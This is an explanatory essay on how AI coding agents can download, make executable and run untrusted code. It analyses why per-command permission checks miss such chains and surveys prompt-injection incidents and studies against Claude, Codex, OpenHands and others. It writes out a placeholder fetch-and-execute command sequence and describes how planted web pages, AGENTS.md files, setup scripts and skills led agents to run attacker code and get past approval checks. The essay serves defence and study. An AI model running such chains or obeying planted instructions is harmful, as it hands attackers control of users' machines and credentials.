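# Download, make executable, run: detecting a dangerous command sequence in AI agents' shell use

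## How an agent uses the shell, and what the three commands do

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and receives their results. Coding agents such as OpenAI's Codex, Anthropic's Claude Code and Cursor do much of their work through the shell, the program on Linux and macOS that runs typed commands. An agent can use the shell to search a project, compile it, run its tests and install the software it needs. It can also download a file from the internet, give that file permission to run, and run it. This sequence is called the fetch-chmod-execute chain. Chmod is the Unix command that changes a file's permissions.

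Downloading a file, making it executable and running it is a common way to install software. Attackers have long delivered malware with commands that look the same. Each command is routine, so developers often let an agent run it without asking for approval. Together, the three commands start code that nobody has examined, with the same access to the machine as the developer has. As Monperrus points out in *Practical Agentic Software Supply Chain Security* (2026), an agent working alone may run dozens of shell commands in one task without a human reviewing each of them.

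### The agent loop

A language model only produces text, so it needs a surrounding program to read that text and carry out actions on a machine. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how this works in Codex.

The program first assembles a prompt containing standing instructions, a list of the tools the model may use, a description of the working directory and of any limits on file and network access, and finally the user's request. The model responds with either a message to the user, which ends the loop, or a tool call, which is a request to use one of the listed tools. Codex's shell tool takes a command and, optionally, a directory to run it in and a time limit. The program runs the command, appends the output to the prompt, and sends the longer prompt back to the model, which picks its next step. One user request can lead to hundreds of tool calls before the final message.

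Some agents, such as the one Docker's *Shell Tool* documents, run each command in a new shell session, so a variable set in one call is gone by the next. Files saved to disk remain, along with their permissions, so the three commands work just as well across several tool calls as on one line.

### Who decides whether a command runs

Before a command reaches the shell, the surrounding program can allow it, ask a person to approve it, or refuse it. Claude Code does this with rules that users write or save. According to Anthropic's documentation, it checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and applies the first one that matches. Claude Code enforces the rules itself, so instructions in the prompt influence what the model tries to do but not what the program permits.

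The allow rules form an allowlist, a list of commands that the agent may run without asking a person. Allowlists tend to grow with use. When Claude Code asks for approval to run a shell command, the user can answer "yes, and don't ask again", and Claude Code then saves a rule that also covers later sessions in the same project. If the approved line joins several commands, Claude Code saves a separate rule for each part that needed approval, up to five.

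The effect of putting a command on the list varies between agents. Cursor normally runs an agent's commands in a sandbox, an environment that limits which files and network addresses a program can reach. According to Cursor's *Terminal* documentation, a command on the allowlist skips the sandbox and runs immediately, so adding it removes both the sandbox's limits and the request for approval. Docker's agent uses a built-in list to label every command safe, destructive or unknown, and it labels ordinary builds, tests and scripts unknown. A setting determines whether the agent asks about unknown commands, refuses them, or runs everything.

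These mechanisms exist because people tire of permission prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes "approval fatigue", in which users stop paying close attention to what they approve. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* later reported that users approve 97% of permission prompts. Anthropic acknowledges that most of those commands were probably harmless, so the figure doesn't prove that users are careless. Still, someone who has just approved thirty commands in a row is less likely to notice a problem with the next one. Since August 2026, Claude Code's individual and team plans have by default used a classifier, a model that evaluates each action, in place of the user's approval.

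### Prompt injection

In Bolin's worked example, the model's first tool call prints a project's README, the file that introduces the software to its users. The text then goes into the prompt, alongside the instructions and the user's request. Codex attaches roles to its messages to indicate how much weight the model should give them, but nothing in the loop itself prevents the model from acting on a sentence it found in a file.

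In a prompt injection attack, an agent treats text in the material it reads as an instruction. Monperrus lists READMEs, documentation pages and dependency lists as places where an attacker can plant a command for the agent to run. The planted command blends in because legitimate READMEs are full of installation commands, and an agent that ignored them all would be of little use. The agent runs commands with the developer's credentials and file permissions.

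An agent can also run harmful code without any injection. If a user asks for a tool and someone has tampered with the server that hosts it, an agent that follows the request exactly will download the tampered copy.

### The three commands

Take a harmless placeholder: a file named tool, on example.org, a domain reserved for use in documentation.

```
curl -o tool example.org/tool
chmod +x tool
./tool
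```

The first command runs curl, which contacts the server and saves whatever the server sends to a file named tool in the current directory. The file's name is set in the command, but its contents come from the server, so nobody can tell from the command's text what has arrived. On a typical Linux system, the file's owner can now read and change it and other users can read it, but nobody can start it as a program yet.

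The second command changes the file's permissions and leaves its contents alone. Unix keeps separate permissions to read, write and execute a file for its owner, for a group of users and for everyone else. The execute bit lets a file run as a program. In a directory listing, the permissions of `tool` would change from `rw-r--r--` to `rwxr-xr-x`. In numeric form, the change is from 644 to 755, where each digit is the sum of 4 for read, 2 for write and 1 for execute. Only the file's owner or the administrator can change its permissions. Since curl ran under the user's account, the user owns the file, and the agent needs no special privilege.

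Nothing inspects the file when its executable bit is set. The bit belongs to the file rather than its contents, so if `curl` later overwrites `tool` with different bytes, the new bytes are executable too.

The third command creates a process, a running program. The prefix `./` points to the current directory, where the shell does not normally look for programs. The shell calls the kernel, the core of the operating system, to load the file, and the kernel checks the execute bit. If the bit is not set, the command fails with the message "Permission denied". Otherwise, the new process runs under the user's identity and inherits the shell's environment variables, which on a developer's machine often include access keys. Unless a sandbox confines it, the process can read the user's documents and saved credentials, change the user's files, open network connections and start other programs.

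That later activity does not pass through the agent as tool calls. Anthropic states that, as a result, a Claude Code rule against reading a certain file does not apply to a script that opens the file itself. Preventing the script from reading the file requires enforcement by the operating system.

### Compiled programs and scripts

How the kernel handles tool depends on its file type. A compiled program consists of machine code, which the processor can execute directly, and on Linux it begins with a few bytes that identify the format. The kernel loads the program into memory, and the processor executes it. In a text editor, such a file looks mostly like gibberish.

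The processor cannot execute a script, which is text in a language such as Bash or Python, so another program, the interpreter, reads it and carries out its instructions. Scripts usually name their interpreter on the first line, after the characters `#!`. When the user types `./tool`, the kernel reads that line, starts the interpreter and passes it the script.

A script can run without the chmod step. The command `bash tool` starts Bash, which is already executable and only needs to read the file, so the file doesn't need an execute bit. Monperrus gives this two-command form, in which curl saves an installation script and Bash then runs it. A shorter form pipes the download straight into a shell without saving a file. A detector that requires chmod will therefore catch compiled programs and scripts started directly, but miss scripts passed to an interpreter.

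Scripts have one advantage for the defender, which is that a person or the agent can read a downloaded script before running it, as Monperrus notes. Inspecting a compiled program takes specialist tools and much more time.

### Why the pattern alone proves nothing

Developers routinely download and run software. Many command-line tools come as a single compiled file, and installing one by hand takes the steps above. Package managers, which install software from organised collections, do much the same without showing the user each step.

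For example, Cursor's sandbox will not start on some Linux systems without an extra security profile. The documentation tells users of those systems to download a package with curl and install it with administrator rights. They don't need chmod, because the package already records its files' permissions. The installation has more system access than the running example, which uses only the user's own account. Cursor also expects agents to download software while they work. Its default list of permitted network addresses for sandboxed commands includes the main package collections, the address of the Rust language's installation script, and GitHub's file hosting, where anyone with an account can publish.

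People who write detection rules run into the same problem. *Ingress Tool Transfer*, a guide from the security company Red Canary to spotting downloads by attackers, says that there are "countless legitimate reasons" for bringing tools onto a machine, and that nearly any attack involves it too. *File Permission Modification in Writable Directory*, a ready-made rule from Elastic, raises an alert when chmod or one of three related commands runs in a directory for temporary files. It has to exempt commands launched by the package manager apt-get, Java, the web server nginx and several other ordinary programs.

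Suppose that one chain in a thousand on developers' machines is malicious (the figure is invented). An alarm that went off at every chain would catch all the malicious ones, but 999 in 1,000 alarms would be false, and people would soon stop reading them.

### The chain as a way of delivering malware

Attackers used this chain of commands long before agents did. The American nonprofit MITRE maintains ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attack methods that security teams use to label what they find. ATT&CK lists the three steps under separate entries rather than as a single method.

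In MITRE ATT&CK, the download falls under *Ingress Tool Transfer* (2017, T1105). That entry lists curl and wget among the usual utilities on Linux and macOS, along with well over a hundred groups, campaigns and malicious programs that have fetched files this way. The chmod step falls under *File and Directory Permissions Modification* (2020, T1222.002), and running the file from a shell falls under the Unix shell entry of *Command and Scripting Interpreter* (2020, T1059.004). The years are when MITRE created the entries, though the methods are older.

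The entries give a partial history of how attackers have used these steps. Skidmap, Linux malware that researchers described in September 2019, hides cryptocurrency mining and used a shell script to download and install its main component. Penquin, covered in a May 2020 report, can set the execute bit on a file it has downloaded. The operators of the KV botnet, a network of hijacked routers that Black Lotus Labs exposed in December 2023, used Bash scripts during installation and made downloaded tools executable. On macOS, Shlayer used curl to save its payload in a temporary directory and chmod to make it executable. The ransomware Qilin also applies `chmod +x` to its own payload, according to MITRE ATT&CK's broader entry on permissions, *File and Directory Permissions Modification* (2018).

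The chmod entry only partly fits the chain. Eight of its fifteen examples involve attackers making their own files executable, as the second command does. But the entry describes permission changes as a way around access controls, to reach protected files, and MITRE ATT&CK lists the technique under Defense Impairment, the category for attempts to weaken a system's defences. In the running example, the user owns the file, so there is no protection to get around.

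MITRE's detection advice already leans towards looking for sequences. For Linux, MITRE ATT&CK's *Detect Ingress Tool Transfers via Behavioral Chain* (2025) recommends looking for curl, wget or a similar program contacting an outside address, followed by an executable file appearing on the disk. The Windows advice includes an adjustment for known good updaters, which do the same thing legitimately.

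The catalogue's download entry describes adversaries bringing tools into an environment that is already compromised, so an intruder has got in some other way and is now typing commands or running scripts. With an agent, nobody needs to have broken in. The user's own software issues the commands from the user's account while doing work the user requested, and the machine may be uncompromised until the third command runs.

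## Why three allowed commands can add up to a forbidden result

Most of the permission rules described so far judge a command by its text. A single-command check, or stateless check, judges each command without using any record of earlier ones. No single-command check can handle `./tool` correctly every time, because whether to allow it depends on information that isn't in the command's text.

### Two histories, one command

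Suppose an agent works in the same directory on the same machine in two different sessions.

| Step | Session A: built from the user's source | Session B: downloaded from a stranger |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `cc -o tool tool.c` | `curl -o tool example.org/tool` |
| 2 | (the compiler has already set the execute bit) | `chmod +x tool` |
| 3 | `./tool` | `./tool` |

In session A, the C compiler `cc` turns the user's own source code into a program, and the agent runs it to see whether it works. Coding agents do this routinely. In session B, the program is whatever the server sent, and we assume it is malicious.

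A single-command check bases its verdict only on the text of the command. The last command is `./tool` in both sessions, so the check must give the same verdict in both. Allowing the command lets the attack in session B succeed, while refusing it stops the agent in session A from running the program it has just built.

Making the check random doesn't help. A check that refused `./tool` at random 70% of the time would stop 70% of the attacks and 70% of the harmless builds. For pairs like this one, the detection rate (the share of dangerous cases that a detector flags) always equals the false-positive rate (the share of harmless cases that it flags).

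Checking an earlier step has the same problem. An agent that has just written its own script may make it executable with `chmod +x tool`, exactly the command used in session B. The same curl command may fetch a legitimate program one day and a tampered one the next. A curl rule can at least check the address against a list of allowed servers, which blocks many unknown servers, but it fails when someone has tampered with a server on the list.

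Wu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *MOSAIC*, put the relation between commands into general form. Each command *c*ᵢ writes some part of the machine's shared state, *P*ᵢ, and reads or acts on some part, *Q*ᵢ. A later command *c*ⱼ depends on *c*ᵢ when *P*ᵢ and *Q*ⱼ overlap:

*i* < *j* and *P*ᵢ ∩ *Q*ⱼ ≠ ∅

In session B, curl writes the file's contents, chmod sets its execute bit, and `./tool` uses both. In session A, the compiler writes the contents and sets the execute bit. A filter that reads only the current command has no record of which program did either.

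Wu and colleagues tested 101 chains of two to four dependent steps on five coding agents, including Claude Code and Codex, with five models. The chains reached their harmful result in 2,439 of 2,525 trials. Adding Semgrep, a scanner that searches code and commands for known bad patterns, lowered the chains' success rate on Claude Code from 96.6% to 86.7%.

A detector also needs to work out the state that past commands produced. *LatentRiskBench* (2026), a test of guards for business agents, includes 100 harmless cases that repeat the action of a harmful case under different circumstances. Guards that judged single actions left in place much of the risk that depended on earlier state, and so did a guard that read the full record of past actions without working out the resulting state. In the running example, the detector has to know that the file the agent is now starting is the one curl wrote,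 not just that curl ran at some point.

### Approving a line part by part

An agent can also put the whole chain on one line:

```
curl -o tool example.org/tool && chmod +x tool && ./tool
```

The `&&` operator runs the next command only if the previous one succeeded. When the three commands are joined this way, the check receives them in order on one line, so it doesn't need a record of earlier commands. Several products nevertheless split the line and check each command separately.

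According to Salesforce, its coding agent Agentforce Vibes automatically approves a compound command only when every command in it is on the user's safe list. Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* describes the same default for Visual Studio Code. JetBrains and Anthropic also describe this default for their agents, Junie and Claude Code. Junie also checks commands nested inside other commands, at any depth.

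Splitting a compound command and checking each part separately prevents a rule that allows `npm test` from also allowing anything an agent types after `npm test &&`. But this check assumes that a series of harmless commands is harmless, so it allows an agent to download a file, make it executable and run it if each command is allowed on its own. A user who approved `curl` in March, `chmod` in May and `./tool` in June, each for a sensible reason, has approved the whole chain without seeing it.

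Agentforce Vibes also asks about every pipe and redirection, whatever the safe list contains, because these operators can change what a command does or help data leak out. This catches the shorter form of the attack, which pipes a download straight into a shell. The line above gets past this check because it writes the file with curl's `-o` option and so contains no pipe or redirection.

Claude Code doesn't require approval for `cd` within the project or for a read-only git command. It does prompt for approval when one line combines the two and `cd` changes to a different directory, because git may run that directory's hooks, which are scripts that git starts automatically. So Anthropic has recognised that two commands that are harmless separately can together run unknown code. But this rule covers only one combination, which someone had to anticipate.

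Visual Studio Code lets users write a rule for the full command line, which could look for the three steps together. The rule won't match if the agent sends the steps as separate tool calls. Microsoft describes automatic approval as "a best-effort convenience, not a security boundary".

*Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) compares agent defences by working out what each design can observe, without running any of them. It distinguishes eight classes of failure in which authorised actions combine into an unauthorised result. Approving tools one at a time catches none of the eight. The two best existing designs in the comparison, which track labelled data from one action to the next, catch seven.

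### Guarding chmod

If no verdict on `./tool` is right, perhaps a person could approve every use of one of the other commands. The obvious choice is `chmod`, since agents need it less often than `curl`.

Seqera's *Command approval* describes an agent that works this way. In its most permissive mode, the agent runs every command without asking except thirteen that Seqera considers dangerous, including chmod. In session B, the agent would download the file, then ask before running chmod. If the user said no, `./tool` would fail because the file wouldn't have the execute bit.

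A script passed to an interpreter, as in `bash tool`, skips the chmod step, however, and Seqera's list includes neither curl nor wget, and neither Bash nor Python. In the permissive mode, a script can therefore arrive and run without a single question. (In the default mode, curl, wget and Python all need approval.)

Compiled programs can also run without a chmod command. Archive formats such as tar store each file's execute bit, so unpacking an archive can produce a program that is ready to run.

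Anthropic reports that in June 2026, 43% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had a rule allowing an interpreter such as Python or Node to run with any arguments. Anthropic considers these rules practically equivalent to allowing every shell command. Claude Code suspends them in auto mode, where a classifier reviews actions, and restores them when the user switches to another mode.

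Chmod is still useful to a detector. It appears in session B but not in session A, and it includes the file's name, so a detector that has recorded the download can link the two commands. An alarm on chmod alone would go off for every script that an agent writes and makes executable.

### What running the file adds

Each of the three commands is routine on its own, but together they let whoever controls the download server choose what code runs on the user's machine.

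Downloading a file, making it executable and running it is worse than most combinations of harmless actions. If an agent reads a password file and then sends a message, the damage is a leaked password. Once the downloaded program `./tool` starts, it can do anything the user's account can do. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) notes that scripts and binaries may do more than their names or the command text suggest. Monitors of tool calls miss this activity, which Shah and Kathrotia (2026) call the "Invocation Abstraction Gap" in *Compositional Exploits in Autonomous Coding Agents*.

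The contents can also change after someone has reviewed them. A user may read an installation script in a browser, find it harmless and tell the agent to download and run it. The agent then fetches the script again, and the server can send a different file. A saved allow rule makes the gap between review and download much longer, because the rule stays in force for months and the server's owner or an intruder can replace the file at any time.

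In 2021, attackers altered a script that customers of the software company Codecov routinely downloaded and ran. The address and the command stayed the same. *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (2026), which blocks shell commands by pattern, cites the incident as its reason for blocking commands that pipe downloads into a shell.

### Five hundred valid requests

In *Agent Control Protocol*, Fernandez (2026) compared a check that has memory with one that doesn't. The protocol gives each request from an agent a risk score. It approves requests that score up to 39, passes those from 40 to 69 to a person, and denies those at 70 or above. In the sixth experiment, one agent made 500 identical requests for a financial transfer, each with a base score of 35, low enough to be approved on its own.

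Both versions used the same scoring code and thresholds. For the stateless version, Fernandez replaced the record of past requests with a stub that always returned zero. He also froze the clock so no request became too old to count.

| Outcome | Stateless | With memory |
|---|---|---|
| Approved | 500 | 2 |
| Passed to a person | 0 | 8 |
| Denied | 0 | 3 |
| Blocked during cooldown | 0 | 487 |

The scores explain the second column. From the third request on, a rule about repeated patterns added 15 points, bringing the score to 50. From the eleventh request on, a rule about request rates added 20 more, bringing it to 70. After three denials, the protocol entered a cooldown and blocked all remaining requests.

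The stateless column needed no experiment, because a function that gets the same input 500 times will return the same output 500 times. The other column depends on thresholds that Fernandez chose, and different thresholds would have let more or fewer transfers through. The comparison still shows that access to the record caused the difference between the columns, since the two versions were otherwise the same.

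The experiment doesn't show that the protocol would catch a download chain. It repeats one action hundreds of times, whereas the chain runs three different actions once each, so repetition counters would stay below their thresholds.

Memory also introduced a new kind of error. In the next experiment, an agent made eleven harmless requests to read public data and then asked for one sensitive transfer. With a clean record, the transfer scored 50 and the protocol referred it to a person. After the eleven reads, it scored 70 and the protocol denied it, although the reads had nothing to do with the transfer. Fernandez fixed this by counting requests separately for each combination of agent, permission and resource. Separate counts work for floods of similar requests, but to detect the chain, a rule has to connect a download, a permission change and a program start, which are different kinds of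 action on the same file.

A later experiment tested Open Policy Agent, a widely used open-source engine that evaluates requests against written rules. Without a count of earlier requests, the engine allowed all ten identical requests. When the calling program supplied a running count, the engine denied requests once the count reached the limit. The engine could therefore apply the rule, but it relied on another component to keep the count correct, and Fernandez points out that nothing in the engine guarantees this. *LEANGUARD* (2026) checks agents' actions against formal policies that can make permission depend on earlier actions, a prior authorisation or what the user has been shown.

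### Chains of harmless tool calls

Li, He and colleagues (2025), in *STAC*, tested sequences of different actions. Their 483 cases contain between two and six tool calls each, in simulated banking, travel, office and other environments. Every call except the last is harmless on its own. In one case, the agent compresses a document, deletes the original as a duplicate, and then deletes all ZIP archives to save space, which destroys the only remaining copy. The last step would have been routine cleanup if the original had still existed.

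Li and colleagues ran the cases on eight models: two versions of GPT-4.1, two Llama models, three Mistral models and one Qwen model. Each agent received a conversation that already contained the earlier calls. An attacker posing as the user then had up to three turns to get the agent to make the last call. On average, the attack succeeded in 80.0% of cases after one turn and 91.2% after three. By then, the success rate was above 90% for seven models and 77.8% for the eighth, Magistral Small. It rarely refused, so they attribute its lower rate partly to its failing at the tasks.

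On 390 of the cases, Li and colleagues also tried to get the same harmful result with a single request and no earlier steps. This worked 72.8% of the time, compared with 95.1% for the full chain. The earlier steps clearly made a difference, but the agents carried out most of the harmful actions even without them.

The defences consisted of extra instructions to the agent. On GPT-4.1, the attack's success rates were as follows.

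| Defence | After one turn | After three turns |
|---|---|---|
| None | 87.4% | 93.4% |
| Summarise the user's overall intent first | 79.3% | 87.0% |
| Weigh harms against benefits before each call | 58.6% | 86.7% |
| ToolShield: guidelines drawn from earlier attacks | 68.5% | 78.1% |

Weighing harms and benefits helped a lot at first, but two turns later the attacker had undone most of the improvement. ToolShield held up better, though it had the advantage of learning from attacks in the same environments.

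In these failures, unlike those of a single-command check, the agent had the whole conversation in its prompt. Two of the defences included an instruction to consider all of it, but the agent still made the wrong decision. A rule that links specific events, such as a download to a path and the start of a program from that path, doesn't depend on the model to connect them.

The 91.2% success rate is probably too high for real attacks. The attacker knew the tools and data in advance, the earlier steps were scripted, and GPT-4.1 was the judge. On 32 tasks with real file and browser servers, where the attacker had to discover what the environment contained, attacks on GPT-4.1 succeeded 35.5% of the time.

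The models in that study are now old, but Shah and Kathrotia found the same weakness in newer ones. Without protection, Gemini 3.5 Flash completed 72.9% of 354 harmful chains, Gemini 3.7 Flash 79.4% and Gemini 3.8 Flash 84.5%. Each generation was better at planning and recovering from errors, which also made it better at completing harmful chains. These are all smaller models from one company, so the trend may not hold for other models.

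Shah and Kathrotia also gave the 32 tools used in the chains to five scanners that inspect one tool at a time. The scanners flagged none of them, which was correct in a sense, because the tools contained no malicious code. The harmless tasks in the same benchmark used the same 32 tools, so flagging any one tool by itself would also have flagged normal work.

### Would a better check on the last command be enough?

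Nothing bad happens in session B until `./tool` runs, so one option is to check only at that moment. Whether this works depends on what information the check can use.

A check that reads only the text of `./tool` can't tell a safe history from a dangerous one, because the command is the same in both. A person reading the text is hardly better off, since people often miss even commands that look dangerous, and `./tool` doesn't. Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work through a coding session in which the research vendor replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers stopped it in 13.6% of cases. They caught about 17% early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more prompts.

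Anthropic's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands, but it also checks whether an action fits what the user asked for, so this result doesn't show that checking one command by itself is enough. When the safety company Apollo Research found attacks that got past the classifier, Anthropic strengthened it mainly by giving it more context about the environment, such as the state of the code repository. Its miss rate on Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%.

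The check could also open the file and examine the program. This is worth doing and catches known malware, but *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (2026) proves that no guard can correctly decide, for every program, whether it performs a harmful action. Adding a harmful action to the end of any program creates a new program that does harm only if the original finishes. A perfect guard could therefore also tell which programs finish, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no general procedure can do that.

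The theorem still allows a guard that lets nothing forbidden through, as long as it sometimes blocks permitted cases. The rate of these mistakes can be arbitrarily close to zero, although no single algorithm can produce such guards for every situation. In practice, inspection can also miss code that hasn't been downloaded yet. A downloaded installer may consist of ten harmless-looking lines, one of which fetches another program after the check has run.

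Finally, the check could use the file's origin, which distinguishes session A from session B. But the command doesn't contain that information, and the file usually doesn't either, so something must have recorded it when curl wrote the file. A check that uses this record still runs at the last step, but it is no longer a single-command check because its result depends on an earlier event.

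## Cases in which agents downloaded and ran harmful code

### A program offered on a web page

In October 2024, Anthropic released a beta version of Claude Computer Use, an agent that controls a whole computer by looking at screenshots and can also run shell commands. A few days later, the security researcher Johann Rehberger tried to make it run malware using only prompt injection. *ZombAIs*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, describes the result of this demonstration, which had no victims. Rehberger wrote a web page and hosted a program that would give him remote control of any machine that ran it.

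Rehberger's first attempts to get Claude to download the program with a shell command failed. Claude objected to the untrusted address and to tools such as wget. He then dropped the commands and put a short, plain request on the page to fetch the file with Firefox and start it. Claude clicked the link. It couldn't find the file in the downloads folder at first, so it ran a shell command to search for it. It then made the file executable with `chmod +x` and ran the program, which connected to Rehberger's server.

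The page contained no shell commands, so a scan for dangerous ones would have found nothing. Claude added the chmod step itself because the program wouldn't start without it. Claude's commands included a search, a permission change and a program start, but no download, because Firefox had done that. To detect the danger, a monitoring system would have had to connect the browser's download with the chmod on the same file. Claude's refusal of the wget version didn't help much, because the same file reached the same disk by another route.

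Rehberger reports one successful run and no success rate, and the model is now two years old. In 2025 he repeated the attack on OpenHands, a coding agent from All Hands AI. According to Embrace The Red's *ZombAI Exploit with OpenHands*, he used the same page and changed only the program behind the link. The user asked OpenHands only to load the website, but it also downloaded the program and ran it. The request would have helped a defender recognize the attack, since loading a page doesn't require starting new software.

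Rehberger also tried a trick that attackers use on people, in which a page gets the visitor to copy commands into a terminal. OpenHands copied and ran them. The attacker supplies the commands in this version, so a check on command text can at least examine them.

He told All Hands AI about the flaw in March 2025, and the company acknowledged his report that month. It didn't answer his inquiry in June, and he published in August. His main advice to users was to run the agent in a sandbox and restrict its outgoing connections. A sandbox wouldn't have stopped the program from starting or protected any code or access keys inside it, but it would have kept the program from reaching the rest of the machine.

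### A download inside a setup script

In Rehberger's demonstrations, the agent started the harmful file itself. In *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine*, Hall and Engelbrecht (2026) used a script for that step. They work with 0DIN, Mozilla's programme for finding security flaws in AI systems. Their attack was also a demonstration, and Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents* calls it a proof of concept.

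A developer gives Claude Code a link to a software project and asks it to get the project running. Claude Code reads the setup notes, installs the listed packages and tries to start the program. The program stops and displays an error message that it needs initialising, with the command to do so. Claude Code runs the command, as a human developer probably would. The command starts a shell script from the project, which looks up a text entry in DNS, the internet's directory of domain names, and passes whatever it finds to Bash to run. In the demonstration, that text gave the attacker an interactive shell under the developer's account.

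Claude Code's commands contained no download, no chmod and no suspicious file name, and the terminal showed two routine lines about the initialisation. Hall and Engelbrecht correctly stress that no scan of the project's files could have found the harmful text, because it was never in the project. But the script, which was on the disk before Claude Code ran anything, contained a line that fetched text from the network and ran it. Someone who opened the script could have seen that it ran text from a stranger's server, though not what that text would be.

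Hall and Engelbrecht want agents to show the user everything a setup command will run, including any scripts it calls and anything those scripts fetch. Showing the fetched text is only useful if the machine then runs exactly that text, without looking up the DNS entry again. An operating-system monitor could have observed more, including the setup script starting Bash and Bash connecting to an outside machine.

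### Package installers that fetch and run

A package installer such as npm, which handles JavaScript packages, downloads code and can run some of it during installation. One ordinary command can therefore have the same effect as downloading a file, making it executable and running it.

Forever Security's *Markdown Is the New Executable*, from October 2026, begins with a real attack. The company's software stopped a coding agent on a customer's machine from installing function-color, an npm package already known to be malicious, before any of the package's code ran. The researchers Gal Weizman and Omer Samet traced the installation to a file named AGENTS.md in the customer's Downloads folder. Developers use files with this name to give coding agents standing instructions for a project, and Codex reads them when it starts. This one looked like ordinary engineering notes.

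Nobody knew how the file had got into the Downloads folder. Weizman and Samet point out that a website can save a file there without the user clicking anything, and they built a page that did so. A website is therefore a plausible source, but they didn't establish that this file came from one.

They then tested the planted file on Codex. When someone opened Codex in the Downloads folder and gave it any task, it changed its own settings and installed the package named in the file. According to Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder*, Codex ran the malware in more than 90% of attempts. That figure measures how often Codex obeyed the file, since most attempts used a harmless stand-in that opens a calculator. The researchers ran the real package only once, in an isolated virtual machine. The file's wording seems to have mattered,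 because Codex refused a short request to install a package, while the planted file buried its request in 13 kilobytes of dull guidelines.

For Claude Code, Weizman and Samet wrote a different file that redirected the agent's traffic to a server they controlled. Claude Code complied in about half of the tests, and in about a fifth of the tests they could also run code in the same session. They found Claude much harder to fool, but the two attacks have little in common, so the 90% and 50% figures aren't a fair comparison of the two products.

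The visible signs in Codex's session were a change to its settings and an install command with the package's name. The name revealed the attack only because someone had already identified the package as malicious. The campaign behind it had gone unnoticed for about two years, during which a check against known malicious names would have missed the package. The settings change may be the better warning, since few coding tasks require an agent to reconfigure itself. The new settings also applied to every later Codex session on the computer.

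Weizman and Samet argue that OpenAI and Anthropic have nothing to patch, because an agent that follows the instruction file in its folder is working as designed. This seems too generous, because OpenAI could treat a folder that any website can write to differently from a project folder. Codex follows an instruction file only in a trusted folder, but Downloads becomes trusted once the user has worked there. The exposure is probably common, since about half of Forever's customers run a coding agent in their Downloads folder.

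An attacker may not need to plant any instructions. In 2026 the startup Pandex examined llms.txt files, in which companies describe their websites and products for AI agents. Schneier (2026) reports in *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* that 120 of the 8,265 files pointed to software packages or domain names that nobody had registered. Pandex registered some of the names and published harmless packages that only contacted its server and recorded which programs had started each installation. Within an hour a machine at a Fortune 500 company contacted the server, and a few dozen more responses followed. The records showed that Claude, Codex and Hermes, an agent from Nous Research, were involved.

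Agents on real company networks downloaded and ran a stranger's harmless code. Pandex also ran its own test, in which it asked the agents to build a project from a vendor's documentation. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* gives rates of 90% or more for two versions of GPT-5, Luna and Sol, and 30% for Claude Opus 4.8 at a medium effort setting.

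Someone else had already used this gap to spread malware. Xakep's *Ошибки в llms.txt вынуждают Claude, Codex и Hermes запускать чужой код* (2026), an article in a Russian security magazine, describes an npx command in the llms.txt file of Clerk, a company that provides login systems. Npx can fetch an npm package and run it at once. The package named in the command did not exist on npm until an unknown attacker registered the name and uploaded malware. Clerk corrected the file after the researchers warned it. It said that the command was safe for agents that had installed the matching program from Clerk's own plugin, but that others could have received the malware. Xakep mentions no confirmed victim.

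Clerk itself had published the instruction, so this was not strictly prompt injection. The agent's command matched the vendor's documentation word for word, and the package came from the usual collection. Only the package's owner was wrong, and someone would have had to look up who had registered the name to notice.

### A controlled test on eighteen models

Each of these cases involves a few products and, mostly, a single attack. *The Dark Side of LLMs* (Lupinacci, Pironti and colleagues, 2025) reports a broader test, run in July 2025, of agents built on 18 models. These included GPT-4o, GPT-4.1, Claude 4 Sonnet and Opus, several Gemini 2 models, and models from Mistral, Meta, Alibaba and DeepSeek, all now old. The agents ran on a Linux virtual machine with an ordinary user's permissions. They had a tool for running commands and short system prompts without special defences.

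The malware reached the agent as encoded text inside the prompt, so the agent did not need to download anything. It had to decode the text into a program file and run it. The researchers delivered the instructions in three ways: directly in the user's message, hidden in a document that the agent retrieved while answering an innocent question, and through a request from another agent.

| Route | Models that ran the malware at least once |
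|---|---|
| User's message | 17 of 18 (94.4%) |
| Hidden text in a retrieved document | 15 of 18 (83.3%) |
| Request from another agent | 18 of 18 (100%) |

These percentages don't measure how often an attack succeeds. Lupinacci and colleagues ran six different prompts up to three times each and counted a model as vulnerable if a single run succeeded. If each attempt had an independent 10% chance of success, the probability of at least one success in 18 attempts would be 1 − 0.9¹⁸, or about 85%. The rates for individual prompts are more informative. The most effective prompt for retrieved documents had a success rate of 77.8%, which is still high.

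Five of the models ran the malware even though they had recognised it as malicious. Some models that had refused the instructions in a message or document followed them when they came from another agent.

The way the agents unpacked the program matters most for detection. In one of the three command sequences, the agent decoded the program, made it executable and launched it. Another sequence used an archive and needed no chmod, and it was part of the most successful prompt for both direct messages and retrieved documents. The encoded program was visible in the agent's prompt and commands, and a monitor could also have detected a newly written file starting as a program.

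Lupinacci and colleagues also gave three of the models a tool meant only for ping, a program that tests network connections. When given instructions in a message or a document, all three added the attacker's commands after the ping command, and the tool ran them. Restricting the agent to one harmless program didn't help, because the tool passed the model's text to a shell unchecked.

### Malicious skills

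The largest group of real attacks comes from skills. ThreatDown's *Weaponizing autonomy* describes a skill as a folder containing a file of instructions for a particular task and sometimes scripts for the agent to run. Anthropic developed the format and published it as an open standard in late 2025. 1Password points out that the format doesn't restrict the instructions, so they can include terminal commands.

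In early 2026 the security company Koi audited 2,857 skills on ClawHub, a marketplace for users of the AI assistant OpenClaw, and found 341 malicious ones. The Hacker News (2026) reports that 335 of them disguised Atomic Stealer, malware that steals data from Macs, as software that the user had to install first. Trend Micro found similar skills on other sites, and their code remained in ClawHub's public repository after the marketplace removed them.

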